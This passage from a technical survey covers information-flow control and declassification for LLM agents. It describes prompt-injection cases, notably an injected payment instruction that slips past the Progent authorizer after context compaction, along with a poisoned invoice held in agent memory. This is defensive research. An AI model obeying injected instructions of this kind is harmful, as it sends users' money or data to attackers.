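The property that FIDES guarantees is called explicit secrecy. Let *g* be the combined effect of one particular sequence of tool calls on the stored data, and write *d*₁ =_L *d*₂ when two versions of the data agree on every public item. Explicit secrecy requires that

*d*₁ =_L *d*₂ ⇒ *g*(*d*₁) =_L *g*(*d*₂).

Because the same *g* appears on both sides, the definition compares what one fixed sequence would do to two versions of the data. It doesn't account for different secrets leading to different sequences. Sending the balance itself would violate the definition, but sending the fixed text "rich!" satisfies it, because the email is the same whatever the balance is.

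Noninterference compares complete runs, so it also rules out the fixed email. Costa and colleagues gave up that protection so that the agent could still do more useful tasks, because noninterference's restrictions on public writes would be the most severe form of label creep. TaintDroid, which tracks private data on Android phones, makes the same tradeoff.

The corresponding gap for integrity lets an attacker influence which action the agent takes without supplying any of the action's text. The Slack planner that chose a channel by counting hidden messages had this weakness. Garby and colleagues also object that a deliberately incomplete guarantee is hard to audit, because an auditor studying a run cannot tell an intended exception from a leak.

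Their alternative is LLMBDA, a small programming language for agents that tracks both kinds of flow and requires the programmer to write each endorsement explicitly. They proved in Lean that all its programs satisfy a form of noninterference when they contain no endorsements. The theorem covers programs that a model generates during a run. It allows one gap, which is that a secret may affect whether a run finishes. For two runs that differ only in secrets, let μ and ν be the probabilities of each result an observer can see, and let div be the probability that a run never finishes. Then

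Δ(μ, ν) ≤ ½ (div(μ) + div(ν)),

where Δ is the statistical distance between the two sets of probabilities. If both runs always finish, the right-hand side is zero and an observer cannot tell them apart. The theorem does not reduce creep, however. A provably sound system still has to stop whenever its labels become too restrictive, so its usefulness depends on keeping unnecessary labels out of the context.

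### Keeping only the labels that mattered

Siddiqui and colleagues reduce creep by testing whether the model needed the untrusted input at all. In one of their examples, a user asks for the population of New York City. A search returns two results, a trusted page that gives 8.4 million and an untrusted one that gives about 8 million. The ordinary rule makes the answer untrusted even though the trusted page is enough. Their method works as follows:

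1. The model answers the question using all the documents.
2. The system tries smaller sets of documents with more permissive labels and measures how likely the same answer remains.
3. If the answer remains likely enough with one of those sets, the model answers again using only that set.
4. The system discards the original answer and returns the new one with the more permissive label.

For the measurement in step 2, let *y* be the answer, *x* the prompt, *C* all the documents, and *C*_L′ the documents whose labels are no more restrictive than L′. The system accepts L′ if

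U(*p*(*y* | *x*, *C*)) − U(*p*(*y* | *x*, *C*_L′)) ≤ λ.

U is the negative of perplexity, a standard measure of how unlikely a text is under a model, and λ is the loss the system tolerates.

Step 3 makes the method safe because the model that produces the final answer receives only the permitted documents. This holds even if the measurement is wrong or an attacker manipulates it. An attacker who controls an untrusted document can influence whether the system returns an answer labelled trusted, but not what that answer contains.

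In a test with 40 agent conversations, 20 outputs could have received a better label. The method found that label for 17 of the 20 with the smaller version of Llama 2, an open model from 2023, and for 19 with the larger one. Asking the model which documents had mattered worked for 9 with the smaller version and 16 with the larger. When a better label was possible, the regenerated answers matched the reference answers about as well as the originals did. The method did worse on news articles, where it found the right label for 57% of the improvable questions with the smaller model and 39% with the larger.

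The method cannot help when the agent needs the untrusted document, and an attacker can exploit this. If distracting text changes the model's answer enough, the trusted documents alone no longer account for it, and the answer keeps its untrusted label. The attacker can then block the action but not control it. The search also requires extra model calls. In the worst case, the number of calls grows exponentially with the number of documents, although a system with only two labels needs very few.

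### Screening the conversation before each action

Zhong, Chen and colleagues (2025) present a system, *RTBAS*, that makes a similar selection before the model acts. It decides in one pass which parts of the conversation the next step needs. They estimate that the search used by Siddiqui and colleagues, by contrast, needs 16 to 64 extra calls for a typical set of four to six security levels.

RTBAS has two ways to decide which parts of the conversation are relevant. One asks a second language model to pick them out. The other runs a small open model over the conversation, measures the model's attention to each part, and uses a trained classifier to decide from those measurements. In both cases, RTBAS joins the labels of the relevant parts and removes everything with a label more restrictive than the joined one. The planner then chooses a tool call based on what is left, and the system asks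 the user for confirmation if the joined label violates the tool's policy.

In Alex's six-step run, a correct screener would mark the stranger's email as irrelevant to the deposit. RTBAS would hide the email, the label for that step would be T, and the payment would go through. Alex would get an unnecessary confirmation request if the screener wrongly kept the email, and the agent might fail if the screener removed an email the task needed. Neither mistake would let the stranger's text reach the planner under a trusted label.

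On AgentDojo without attacks, RTBAS reduced the share of completed tasks by 10% with the model as screener and by 7.4% with the attention method. It did slightly better than an agent with no defence on workspace and travel tasks, but completed only 22% of Slack tasks with the model and 33% with the attention method. Many Slack tasks require the agent to read an untrusted website and act on its content, so the screener correctly kept that content, along with its label. Zhong and colleagues consider such tasks inherently unsafe without a user's confirmation. Their test had no user to confirm the calls and skipped them, so the Slack scores understate what RTBAS could do with a user present.

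A second test used 37 tasks involving private data in shopping, payments and flight booking. An agent that asked for confirmation of every tool call did so unnecessarily in 29.7% of cases. RTBAS lowered that rate to 8.1% with model-based screening and 16.2% with attention-based screening. But in the banking suite, model-based screening raised the average cost of a task from 1.5 to 3.2 cents and the time from 4.4 to 9.7 seconds.

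### Forked conversations and subagents

An agent can read untrusted text in a separate conversation instead of working out afterwards which text mattered. LLMBDA has two commands for this. `fork` copies the current conversation, does some work in the copy, and then restores the original. `clear` empties a conversation. It also resets the conversation's label if no secret or untrusted data determined whether the command ran. Using both, an agent can read a stranger's email in a fresh conversation, keep the result and discard the rest.

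If the agent does step 3 of Alex's run this way, the main conversation never contains the emails and its label stays T. The agent can then pay the deposit, delete the draft and pass along a summary of the mail. The summary is still labeled U, so the main planner must handle it without reading it. If the planner reads the summary to decide what to do next, the planner's context becomes untrusted.

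Isolation therefore removes accidental label creep but leaves real dependence on untrusted data in place. The separate conversation resembles the quarantined model described earlier, but it does not have to give up all its tools. In *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026), the planner can start subagents that each work on part of a task. A subagent's label rises as it reads, without changing the main agent's label. After reading an untrusted page, the subagent can still use any tool whose policy accepts its current label.

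Zhou and colleagues tested their system, ELBA, on AgentDojo's Slack tasks with four recent models. With policies on, it completed roughly twice as many tasks as CaMeL. All the models resisted every standard attack even without policies, so the researchers forced any subagent that read an injection to obey it. Up to 42% of these attacks succeeded without policies, and none succeeded with them. But the policies also reduced task completion under attack from 67–76%, depending on the model, to 40–48%, so they still blocked a good deal of legitimate work even with recent models and isolated subagents.

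Retries can also spread the untrusted label. If a generated program fails after reading untrusted data, the error message may contain some of that data, and a planner that reads the message to fix the program becomes untrusted. Randori, an agent by Garby and colleagues written in LLMBDA, avoids this by first testing the program on an artificial copy of the world, where all tool results are safe to trust. It runs the program on real data only after the program works in the copy.

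The results on AgentDojo's banking tasks suggest that this helps even without exceptions. In unattacked runs using the model MiMo-v2.5, Randori completed 54.2% with endorsements switched off and 64.6% with them on, while CaMeL completed 37.5% with its policies on. There were only 16 different tasks, so the uncertainty is more than 20 percentage points either way. Randori also enforces only some of CaMeL's policies. Practice helps only if the artificial world is enough like the real one to expose the program's mistakes.

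### Labels in long-term memory

A subagent's conversation can be discarded when its work is done, but many agents keep information for later. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes an agent that retrieves an invoice on Monday, in which an attacker has put a false account number. On Tuesday the agent is asked to "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday". If it stored the invoice without its label, Tuesday's planner could treat the invoice as its own reliable memory. If it kept the label and loaded the invoice into the conversation, Tuesday's context would become untrusted before any work began.

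SPA stores the value, its label and a short description separately. The planner sees only the description, such as "an invoice from Acme", and writes a complete plan that refers to the stored item. The system retrieves the invoice and its original label only when it runs the plan. The planner stays trusted from one day to the next, as long as the descriptions contain no text from an attacker.

To test this, Girrens and Wang turned AgentDojo tasks into sequences of requests in which later ones depend on earlier results. With label checks on, attacks succeeded in 0.2% of cases. When a stored result was available and needed, the agent reused it 89.9% of the time, compared with 95.4% without the checks, so hiding the stored values did little to prevent reuse. But the agent had much more difficulty using those values in actions. The checks cut the share of completed tasks from 62.5% to 35.3% on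 these sequences, and from 53.0% to 29.0% on the original single-request tasks.

Most of the loss came from plans that passed untrusted tool results to actions requiring trusted data. Paying the Acme invoice is one example, because the account number that was untrusted on Monday is still untrusted on Tuesday. As an agent remembers more, it will accumulate more data that it can refer to but can't act on unless someone endorses it.

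### When a summary replaces the conversation

When a conversation grows too long for a model to process, many agent programs perform compaction, in which a model summarizes the earlier conversation and the agent continues from the summary. Under the usual rule for model output, the summary is untrusted if the conversation contained even one untrusted email, so compaction does not reduce label creep.

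If the program loses track of who wrote what, it can make the opposite mistake and treat a stranger's words as trusted. Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, studied Claude Code and Codex, coding agents from Anthropic and OpenAI. In all 1,108 automatic compactions they recorded, the program inserted the summary as a user message. This matters to defences that treat user messages as the user's own words, such as Progent, which uses them to decide which tool calls to permit.

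In one example, a user asks a banking agent about spending in March. A transaction description contains an instruction to pay an attacker, and Progent blocks the payment because the user did not ask for one. After compaction, the summary lists the blocked transfer as unfinished work. Progent then treats it as the user's request and permits a transfer to the attacker's account.

Progent normally writes its policy once, at the start of a session. Fei and colleagues modified it to write a new policy for each request, because the agent completed only 12% of later tasks with a fixed policy, compared with 68% when the policy could change. The attack therefore applies to their modified version of Progent, although they note that some deployed systems also judge each action against the user's messages.

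Better summaries only partly solve the problem. The strongest models usually marked injected instructions as suspicious but rarely marked false information written as ordinary data. In one test, the user had stated which account should receive the rent, and an attacker's notice gave a different one. Policies based on the summary allowed payment to the attacker's account in 91% of cases with one policy-writing model and 59% with another, while policies based on the user's original words never allowed it.

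Fei and colleagues prove a general limit for any authorizer that works from text alone. Let P_L be the distribution of the text it receives when a legitimate source wrote a certain record, and P_A the distribution when an attacker wrote it. If *p*_L and *p*_A are the probabilities that the authorizer accepts the record's value in each case, then

*p*_L − *p*_A ≤ TV(P_L, P_A),

where TV is the total variation distance, the largest difference between the probabilities that the two distributions give to any event. If the attacker imitates a legitimate record perfectly, the distance is zero, and the authorizer must accept both records equally often. Neither a stronger model nor a better prompt can change this, because the missing information is who wrote the text.

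One remedy is to give the agent and the authorizer different inputs. The program attaches a cryptographic tag to each user message when it arrives and keeps an exact copy when the conversation is compacted into a summary. The agent reads the summary, while the authorizer receives only the tagged messages. Ordinary code first checks that these messages are genuine, complete and in order. If any check fails, the agent may not call any tools, so an attacker can block the policy but cannot rewrite it. No attacker's action succeeded in 40 AgentDojo runs under attack, and the system also withstood eight attacks designed against it.

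The tags preserve what the user said, but they cannot show whether a value is genuine when the user left the agent to get it from a document. If Alex asks the agent to pay whatever account the landlord's letter gives, the system will treat a well-forged letter the same as a real one unless it can authenticate where the letter came from.

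## Four questions to ask of any exception: what, who, where and when

To pay the account in the landlord's letter, the agent needs an exception that allows this payment without allowing much else. Researchers had the same problem with programs that handle secrets long before agents existed. A login page, for example, has to reveal a little about each password, because rejecting a guess shows that the guess was wrong. Noninterference forbids this, so researchers proposed many weaker definitions of security, each meant to prevent a different kind of abuse.

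*Dimensions and Principles of Declassification* (Sabelfeld and Sands, 2005) sorts these definitions by four questions: what information a program releases, who controls the release, where in the system it happens, and when. The extended journal version, *Declassification* (2009), also sketches how the questions apply to endorsement.

In the programs below, `secret` holds confidential data and outsiders can read `public`. The word `declassify` marks a deliberate release and has no other effect on the computation.

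### What the program releases

Sabelfeld and Sands describe an observer's knowledge by which values of the secret the observer cannot tell apart. Someone who knows only whether a number is odd or even can tell 3 from 4 but not 3 from 5. Write *m* ~ *n* if the policy requires *m* and *n* to look the same, and let *s*(*m*) be the program's public output when the secret is *m*. The program releases no more than the policy allows if, for all *m* and *n*,

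*m* ~ *n* ⇒ *s*(*m*) = *s*(*n*).

Suppose the policy allows outsiders to learn whether the secret is odd or even. The program `public = secret % 2`, which outputs the remainder after division by 2, passes. The program `public = secret % 4` fails because it outputs 3 when the secret is 3 and 1 when the secret is 5, although both secrets are odd. If ~ relates every value to every other, the condition is noninterference. In both cases ~ is an equivalence relation, but for programs that take functions as inputs, researchers also use partial equivalence relations, which need not relate every value to itself.

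Delimited release, which Sabelfeld and Andrew Myers introduced in 2004, lets programmers state such a policy inside the program. The expressions they mark with `declassify` are called escape hatches. Take any two starting states *s* and *t* that agree on all public data. The program *P* passes if

(*e*(*s*) = *e*(*t*) for every escape hatch *e*) ⇒ *P*(*s*) =_L *P*(*t*),

where =_L means that the public results are the same. For example, this program releases the average of two secret salaries and passes:

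```
public = declassify((ana + ben) / 2)
```

It fails if someone adds a line at the top:

```
ana = ben
public = declassify((ana + ben) / 2)
```

If Ana earns 40 and Ben earns 60, the second program outputs 60. If they swap salaries, it outputs 40. The true average is 50 in both cases, so the program has released Ben's salary labelled as an average.

Delimited release ignores how hard it is to compute one piece of information from another. Suppose the policy allows a program to release a hash, or scrambled version, of a password, and no two passwords have the same hash. The program may then release the password itself, because someone with unlimited computing time could work it out from the hash.

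The condition also ignores which line of the program releases the data:

```
if True:
    public = secret * secret
else:
    public = declassify(secret * secret)
```

This passes, although the marked line never runs and the leak comes from an unmarked line. A reviewer who checked only the marked lines would miss the leak.

### Who controls the release

Sabelfeld and Sands give the example of a policy that allows a shop to release at most four digits of a customer's card number with each purchase. If an attacker can choose the digits, four purchases are enough to reveal a 16-digit number. Each release follows the policy, because it limits what the shop may reveal but not who picks the digits.

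One condition that covers this is robust declassification, which requires that an attacker who interferes with a program learn no more than one who only watches. Write *P*_a(*s*) for what the attacker sees when the secret is *s* and the attacker supplies input *a*. For all secrets *s* and *t* and all inputs *a* and *b*,

*P*_a(*s*) = *P*_a(*t*) ⇒ *P*_b(*s*) = *P*_b(*t*).

The program `public = declassify(card[choice])` fails if the attacker sets `choice`, because the attacker then controls which digit is released. If two cards have the same first digit but different second digits, the attacker can't tell them apart when `choice` picks the first digit but can when it picks the second. A program that always releases the last four digits passes.

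Robustness accepts any leak that attackers cannot influence, including `public = declassify(card)`, which releases the whole card number. Another approach to the "who" question records an owner in each label and lets only the owner release the data, but an owner can also release too much.

### Where the release happens

"Where" can mean a place in the lattice or a place in the code. A policy on the lattice might let secret data flow to a special declassifier level and from there to the public level, but never directly from secret to public. Researchers call this intransitive noninterference because allowing each of the two steps does not allow the direct flow.

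A policy on the code allows releases only at marked lines. One such condition is gradual release, which Broberg, van Delft and Sands (2015), in *The Anatomy and Facets of Dynamic Policies*, express through what an observer can rule out. Let *K*(*t*) be the set of starting states that the observer can rule out after seeing the outputs *t*, and let *e* be the next visible event. If *e* is not a marked release, then

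*K*(*t* · *e*) = *K*(*t*).

Knowledge may therefore grow only at marked releases. Researchers disagree about the details even within this one dimension. Sun, Tang and Chen (2011), in *A New Enforcement on Declassification with Reachability Analysis*, compared gradual release with two other conditions on a set of small programs. One was WHERE, from Mantel (2007), in *Controlling the what and where of declassification in language-based security*, and the other was their own, where-security. These are four of the programs, with the variables renamed (`spare` is also secret):

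| Program | WHERE | Gradual release | Where-security |
|---|---|---|---|
| `spare = secret`, then `public = declassify(spare)` | Pass | Pass | Pass |
| `public = declassify(secret)`, then `public = secret` | Fail | Pass | Pass |
| `public = secret`, then `public = declassify(secret)` | Fail | Fail | Pass |
| A marked release that never runs, then `public = secret` | Fail | Fail | Fail |

WHERE requires every unmarked step to satisfy noninterference on its own, so it rejects any unmarked copy of the secret. Gradual release accepts the copy in the second program because the observer already knows the secret by then. Where-security mainly compares the final results of runs that declassified the same values, so it also accepts the third program, which leaks the secret one line too early.

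### When the release happens

Sabelfeld and Sands found three kinds of condition on timing. The first ties the release to another event, such as a shop handing over a software key only after it has confirmed payment. The second requires that extracting the secret take an impractically long time, which would distinguish releasing a password's hash from releasing the password itself. The third allows a leak if its probability is small enough.

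Ascari, D'Osualdo and colleagues (2026), in *Violet*, a recent system for proving programs secure, give a precise condition for keeping a secret until its release. They treat a run as a log of public outputs and declassified values. Cut the log after *n* entries, and consider only runs in which the program has so far declassified the same values *d*. Let *O* be the set of public outputs possible at that point, *S* the set of possible secrets, and *R* the set of output-secret pairs that can occur together. For every *n* and *d*, the condition requires

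*R* = *O* × *S*.

Every remaining secret must be compatible with every remaining output. Someone who knows *d* then learns nothing more about the secret from the outputs.

This program, adapted from theirs, passes:

```
declassify(secret % 4)
public = secret % 2
```

The first line reveals the secret's remainder after division by 4, which determines whether the secret is odd or even. Swapping the two lines makes the program fail the condition, because after the first step the public output reveals whether the secret is odd, though the program has declassified nothing. Both versions pass if the condition is checked only at the end of the run, because that check covers only what the program releases, and by then each version has released the same information.

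A "when" condition alone has gaps too. A rule that forbids releasing any key before payment would still let a program wait for one customer to pay and then publish every key the company has ever sold. Sabelfeld and Sands therefore hoped that researchers would combine policies from all four dimensions. They left out "how" because they thought combinations of "what", "where" and "when" covered it. They also left out "why", which designers have to settle before anyone writes code.

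### Four checks on the definitions themselves

A definition of safe release can itself be flawed, so Sabelfeld and Sands proposed four principles for checking one.

Semantic consistency requires the verdict to stay the same when a programmer replaces code containing no releases with other code that behaves identically. Some definitions fail this requirement because they examine a program's wording. Suppose a policy allows a secret to leave only through a function *f*, and *f* returns its input unchanged. A definition that looks for the name *f* would accept the output *f*(`secret`) but reject `secret`, although the two values are the same.

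Under the conservativity principle, a program with no declassification is secure exactly when it satisfies noninterference. A program that sets `public` to zero if `secret > secret` leaks nothing, since the condition is never true. But a definition of security that relies on a simple automatic check may violate the principle by rejecting this program because it branches on a secret.

Monotonicity of release requires that marking another release never make a secure program insecure. Suppose a policy allows a program to declassify an encrypted message or its key, but not both. A program declassifies the key and also marks a harmless constant as a release of the message. A definition of security that counts marks without checking what they reveal violates monotonicity, because it rejects this program but accepts it once the programmer removes the harmless mark.

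Non-occlusion requires that a declassification never hide another leak. Sabelfeld and Sands invented a naive definition of security to show why the other three principles are not enough. It accepts a program if any two runs that differ only in their secrets either look the same to outsiders or include at least one run that declassifies something. This definition satisfies the other three principles, but it accepts a program that declassifies one harmless value and then leaks everything else.

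Sabelfeld and Sands checked ten definitions, including the naive one, and eight failed at least one principle. The eight included delimited release and a form of intransitive noninterference, each of which Sabelfeld or Sands had helped to develop. Delimited release failed non-occlusion because of programs like the earlier one in which the marked line never runs. Sabelfeld and Sands argued many of these verdicts informally and did not consider the principles mandatory. A failed check is a reason to look for a weakness and to explain why it is acceptable.

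### The birth-date program

Schoepe, Murray and Sabelfeld (2020), in *VERONICA*, a method for proving that programs with several parallel threads keep their secrets, give a clear example of occlusion. The policy lets a program release the day and month of a person's birth but not the year. In Python-like form, the program is:

```
if birth_year > 2000:
    public = declassify(birth_day)
else:
    public = declassify(birth_month)
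```

A simple checker tests whether each declassified value is either the day or the month. It always is, so the program passes. But the program chooses which one to output based on the year. If it outputs 25, the number must be a day, so the person was born after 2000. If it outputs 7, anyone who knows that the birthday is 25 July can tell that the person was born in 2000 or earlier. The policy allows everyone to know the day and month, so we cannot assume that few people do.

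VERONICA's general security condition has the same gap. It lets an observer's knowledge grow only at declassifications and requires each declassification to follow the policy, but it does not directly limit what the observer learns from them. Schoepe and colleagues say that the condition satisfies the other three principles but not this one. They also prove that their checks can enforce delimited release if the program never branches on a secret that the policy keeps hidden. Delimited release rejects the birth-date program because the program's output can differ for two people who have the same birthday but different birth years.

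Bay and Askarov (2020), in *Reconciling progress-insensitive noninterference and declassification*, describe a less obvious case, an exception meant to let a program reveal that a block of code has finished and nothing else. If outsiders cannot see the end of the block, a careless rule might apply the exception to the next step they can see. Suppose that step sets `public` to 0 if a secret is positive and to 1 otherwise. The careless rule would accept this, although the output also reveals whether the secret is positive. Bay and Askarov therefore set separate limits on what an observer may learn from an event's existence and from its content.

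Passing the check for non-occlusion, the fourth principle, cannot be a complete proof. Sun and colleagues proved that where-security satisfies the first three principles, but argued that nobody can formally prove the fourth. Such a proof would need an agreed definition of a leak, and the principles are meant to test such definitions.

### The same questions for endorsement

Sabelfeld and Sands suggest that the four questions also apply to endorsement. Here is one way to answer them for Alex's request to put a meeting from the last three emails in the calendar:

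| Question | A possible answer |
|---|---|
| What may the system treat as trusted? | Whether there is a meeting request, and its date, time and participants |
| Who controls the exception? | Alex, through the request, and not the sender of an email |
| Where does the exception apply? | Only between the model that reads the emails and the calendar tool |
| When does it apply? | After Alex makes the request, until the agent has dealt with these three emails |

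Each answer prevents a misuse that the others would allow. Without the limit on where the exception applies, the agent could reuse the endorsed date in a payment. Without the limit on time, the agent could add another meeting because of an email that arrives next month. For other tasks, it might be more natural for the exception to apply only after the system has verified the sender's digital signature.

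Birgisson, Russo and Sabelfeld (2010), in *Unifying Facets of Information Integrity*, define delimited endorsement, the counterpart of delimited release. Let *m*₁ and *m*₂ be two starting states that agree on all trusted data, and let *P* be the program. The program passes if

(*e*(*m*₁) = *e*(*m*₂) for every endorsed expression *e*) ⇒ *P*(*m*₁) =_T *P*(*m*₂),

where =_T means that the trusted results are the same. With an endorsement added, the earlier program for Alex's request looks like this:

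```
emails = read_emails(3)
found = endorse(quarantined_model("Find a meeting request", emails))
if found.exists:
    create_event(found.date, found.time, found.participants)
```

Suppose two mailboxes contain different emails but produce the same value of `found`. The program then makes the same calendar entry for both, so it passes. It would fail if another line deleted a calendar entry whenever an email contained the word "urgent", because that word could change the calendar without affecting `found`.

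Birgisson and colleagues enforce the condition with a monitor that runs alongside the program. At each endorsement, the monitor checks that the expression still has the value it had at the start. For data that arrives during the run, an extension uses the most recent input for the comparison. These checks prevent a program from replacing an approved value with another just before endorsing it, the trick that exposed Ben's salary. The monitor also refuses to endorse anything inside a branch that depends on untrusted data, which rules out the integrity version of the birth-date program. The first check assumes that an expression always gives the same result for the same data, so an agent using it would have to save the quarantined model's answer rather than query the model again.

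### Where secrecy and integrity stop being mirror images

Delimited endorsement limits how a stranger can affect the calendar, but it cannot guarantee that the entry is right. Suppose the program adds a week to every date before it creates the event. The stranger has no more influence than before, and the program still passes, but Alex will miss the meeting. Birgisson and colleagues cite Sabelfeld and Myers's observation that a system can damage integrity by computing incorrectly, without any outside interaction. Strong integrity therefore requires proof that the program is correct, which goes beyond tracking who influenced it.

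Birgisson and colleagues distinguish two kinds of rule about what a program must preserve. Value invariance requires something to be the same at the end of a run as at the start, such as the existing entries in Alex's calendar. Predicate invariance requires a property that held at the start to hold at the end, such as the absence of overlapping meetings. Neither can generally replace the other, because value invariance compares two values, while predicate invariance tests a property of each state separately.

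They combine both in a general rule with two expressions, *e*₁ and *e*₂, and a test *Q*. If a run starts in state *m* and ends in state *m*′, it must satisfy

*Q*(*m*(*e*₁), *m*′(*e*₂)).

For value invariance, the two expressions are the same and *Q* is equality. For predicate invariance, *Q* is "if the first is true, so is the second". The rule can also express other correctness requirements, such as requiring a counter to increase during the run.

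No invariant can express noninterference, because an invariant applies to one run at a time and noninterference compares runs. But keeping a trusted file unchanged requires an invariant. Noninterference allows a trusted program to read the file and overwrite it with two copies of its contents, because no untrusted data is involved.

One monitor can still enforce both invariants and information flow. Just before the program ends, the monitor checks the invariants and stops the program if one fails. Birgisson and colleagues proved that, for invariants alone, this never blocks a correct program. The information-flow part is less exact, since it blocks a program that copies untrusted data into a trusted variable and immediately overwrites that variable with zero, even though the data doesn't affect the result. Stopping a program at the end also can't undo a message it has already sent, so the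 researchers suggest checking before each output as well.

The "who" and "when" questions do not carry over neatly either. On "who", Sabelfeld and Sands argue that declassification and endorsement are both privileged operations, so both may need the same protection from untrusted influence, whereas a strict mirror image would call for opposite rules. On "when", a secret can reasonably be called safe because extracting it would take too long, but they found it less clear how a guarantee that data stays untrusted only for so long would be useful.

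### Asking the questions at each level of a policy

Ten years after the original classification, Broberg and colleagues, including Sands, criticized it. They argue that "what" is largely independent of the other three questions, while many uses of "where" and "when" coincide. For example, one can say that the program that copies a secret just before its marked release leaks it on the wrong line or leaks it too early. They also find the two senses of "where" only remotely related.

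They propose asking the questions separately at three levels of a policy. At level 0 is a set *F* of flow rules that could ever be in force. At level 1, a function δ: *S* → *F* picks the current rule using some information in *S*, such as the line the program is running or the time. Level 2 controls how that information may change. Formally, it is a function μ: *M* → 2^(*S* × *S*), which uses further information in *M* to determine the permitted changes. For Alex's request, the levels might look like this:

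| Level | Example | Questions that apply |
|---|---|---|
| 0: possible rules | Either nothing in the emails may affect the calendar, or only the answer and meeting details may | What, and where in the lattice |
| 1: current rule | The looser rule applies while the agent handles Alex's request | Who, where and when |
| 2: changes to the choice | Only Alex can start such a request | Who, where and when |

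The "who" question now comes up twice, and the answers can differ. A system might correctly limit an exception to Alex's requests but store the record of those requests in a file the agent can edit. If an injected instruction then made the agent add a false request to that file, the level 1 check would approve the action because of the weakness at level 2.

Broberg and colleagues also argue that researchers use the word "declassification" too loosely, since people declassify data, not policies. They distinguish relabelling, which gives the original data a less restrictive label, from copying release, which puts a copy under such a label and leaves the original protected. This distinction helps explain the disagreement over the program that declassifies a secret and then copies it again without marking the second copy. That copy is harmless under relabelling, because the data is already public,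 but it is a leak under copying release, which covers only the marked copy.

In an agent, relabelling would mean endorsing the full text of a stranger's email, while copying release would mean endorsing only a copy of the date in it.

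## Keeping the attacker from steering the exception

A narrow exception can still do harm if an attacker chooses what passes through it or when. Suppose Alex's company lets the agent send one number, the final quarterly sales total, to outside partners. A stranger might get the agent to send a different secret number instead, or to send the total before the company has announced it. The shop that reveals four digits of a card number with each purchase has the same weakness if an attacker can pick which digits.

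### Robust declassification

*Robust declassification* (Zdancewic and Myers, 2001) introduced the requirement that an attacker who interferes with a system learn no more than one who only watches. If a system meets this requirement, a reviewer has to check only what it releases when nobody interferes, rather than think through every possible attack.

Zdancewic and Myers described systems abstractly, as states and the steps between them. Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic, in *Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness*, a journal article from 2006, applied the idea to programs such as this one, adapted from theirs:

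```
if send:
    public = declassify(total)
```

An attacker who can change `send` controls whether the program releases anything, and one who can get another secret copied into `total` controls what it releases. If the attacker can do neither, the release is robust, because nothing else affects it.

Robustness therefore depends on what a particular attacker can read and change. There are four combinations:

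| | Attacker cannot change it | Attacker can change it |
|---|---|---|
| **Attacker can read it** | The company's published price list | The attacker's own email |
| **Attacker cannot read it** | Priya's sales preview | A model's private summary of the preview and the attacker's email |

An attacker may control code as well as data. Robustness grew out of research on splitting one program across several computers, some of which might belong to an attacker. The 2006 definition therefore uses programs with holes where the attacker can insert code. In an agent, code that a model writes after reading a stranger's email would fill such a hole.

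### Why the test compares four runs

Robustness means that if one attack cannot tell two secrets apart, no other attack can either. Here are the four runs for the program above, with two possible sales totals and an attacker who controls `send`:

| Secret | Attacker sets `send` to false | Attacker sets `send` to true |
|---|---|---|
| Total is 4 million | Nothing | 4 million |
| Total is 5 million | Nothing | 5 million |

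The attacker can tell the two totals apart when `send` is true but not when it is false, so the program fails. If only trusted code could set `send`, the attacker's choice would make no difference and the program would pass.

Two runs can show that a program violates noninterference, but not that it violates robustness. Cecchetti, Myers and Arden (2017) explain in *Nonmalleable Information Flow Control* that a tester has to vary the secret to find a release and vary the attack to find out whether the attacker influenced it. The two runs with `send` set to true show only that the program releases the total, which may be its purpose. The two runs with a total of 4 million show only that the attacker changed the output, which would also happen in a harmless program that repeats whatever the attacker types.

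They also found that this test rejects some safe programs because an attacker can fail to use an opportunity to learn a secret. Suppose a program displays one of two messages supplied by the attacker, depending on whether a secret is true. The attacker learns the secret only if the two messages differ. The program makes the same release either way, so Cecchetti and colleagues leave "inept" attacks, such as supplying the same message twice, out of the comparison.

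### Checking both the data and the decision

Nobody can test every pair of secrets against every pair of attacks, so practical systems check labels instead. At each declassification, both the data and the decision to release it must have enough integrity. With the two levels T (trusted) and U (untrusted), the condition is

*i*_data ⊔ *i*_decision = T.

In the example, *i*_data is the integrity label of `total` and *i*_decision is that of `send`. If a system checked only the data, an attacker could choose when the system releases the total, and if it checked only the decision, the attacker could replace the total with another secret. Myers and colleagues proved that making this kind of check before the program runs guarantees robustness.

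A single line between trusted and untrusted assumes that everyone fears the same attacker. Chong and Myers, in *Decentralized Robustness*, extended the definition to people who distrust one another. Their method, which Cecchetti and colleagues generalize, turns a list of those who could have influenced something into a list of readers and compares the two. Let *W* be everyone who could have influenced the data or the decision, *R* the people who may read the data before the release, and *R*′ those who may read it afterwards. With lists of people as labels, the rule amounts to

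*R*′ ∩ *W* ⊆ *R*.

So nobody who influenced a release may gain access through it. The rule forbids the agent from sending Marco the sales preview if his email prompted it to do so, even if Alex's organisation trusts him in other matters.

### Qualified robustness and its gap

Some useful programs cannot be robust. A login page, for example, has to let a stranger's guess affect what it reveals, because it reveals whether the guess is correct. Myers and colleagues therefore added an endorsement operation that lets a programmer mark the guess as trusted. The result is a weaker guarantee called qualified robustness, which allows untrusted code and data a limited ability to affect the release of information.

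But the languages that enforced robustness placed no limits on the secrecy of the data that a program endorses. Cecchetti and colleagues show how this can defeat a password check:

```
def check(guess):
    g = endorse(guess)
    return declassify(g == password)
```

Suppose the programmer labels `guess` as secret, which seems prudent. Another part of the program may then call `check(password)`, either by mistake or because someone malicious wrote it. Passing the secret password into the secret `guess` breaks no secrecy rule, and the endorsement satisfies the integrity rule. The check succeeds, so someone who never knew the password gets in.

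In another example, Alice and Bob send sealed bids to an auctioneer they both trust. Neither bid may become public unless Alice and Bob both agree. The auctioneer endorses Alice's bid and passes it on, still sealed. Bob cannot read it, but his program can add 1 to the hidden number and submit the result as his own bid. The auctioneer endorses this bid too, then opens both, and Bob wins by the smallest possible margin. The final release passes the robustness check because both bids count as trusted by then.

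### Transparent endorsement and nonmalleable information flow

In both examples, the system endorses something that its supposed author could not have read, which Cecchetti and colleagues call an opaque write. Their remedy, transparent endorsement, lets a system endorse data only if the people who could have written it could also read it. The program can then no longer pass the password in place of the guess, because the person logging in must be able to read the guess, and Bob's bid cannot contain a number computed from Alice's, because Bob must be able to read his own bid.

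For lists of people, let *W* be everyone who could have influenced the data, *W*′ those whose influence the label still records after the endorsement, and *R* everyone who may read both the data and the information behind the decision to endorse it. The rule becomes

*W* ⊆ *W*′ ∪ *R*.

An endorsement may therefore remove a person's name from the record of influences only if that person could read what the system is endorsing.

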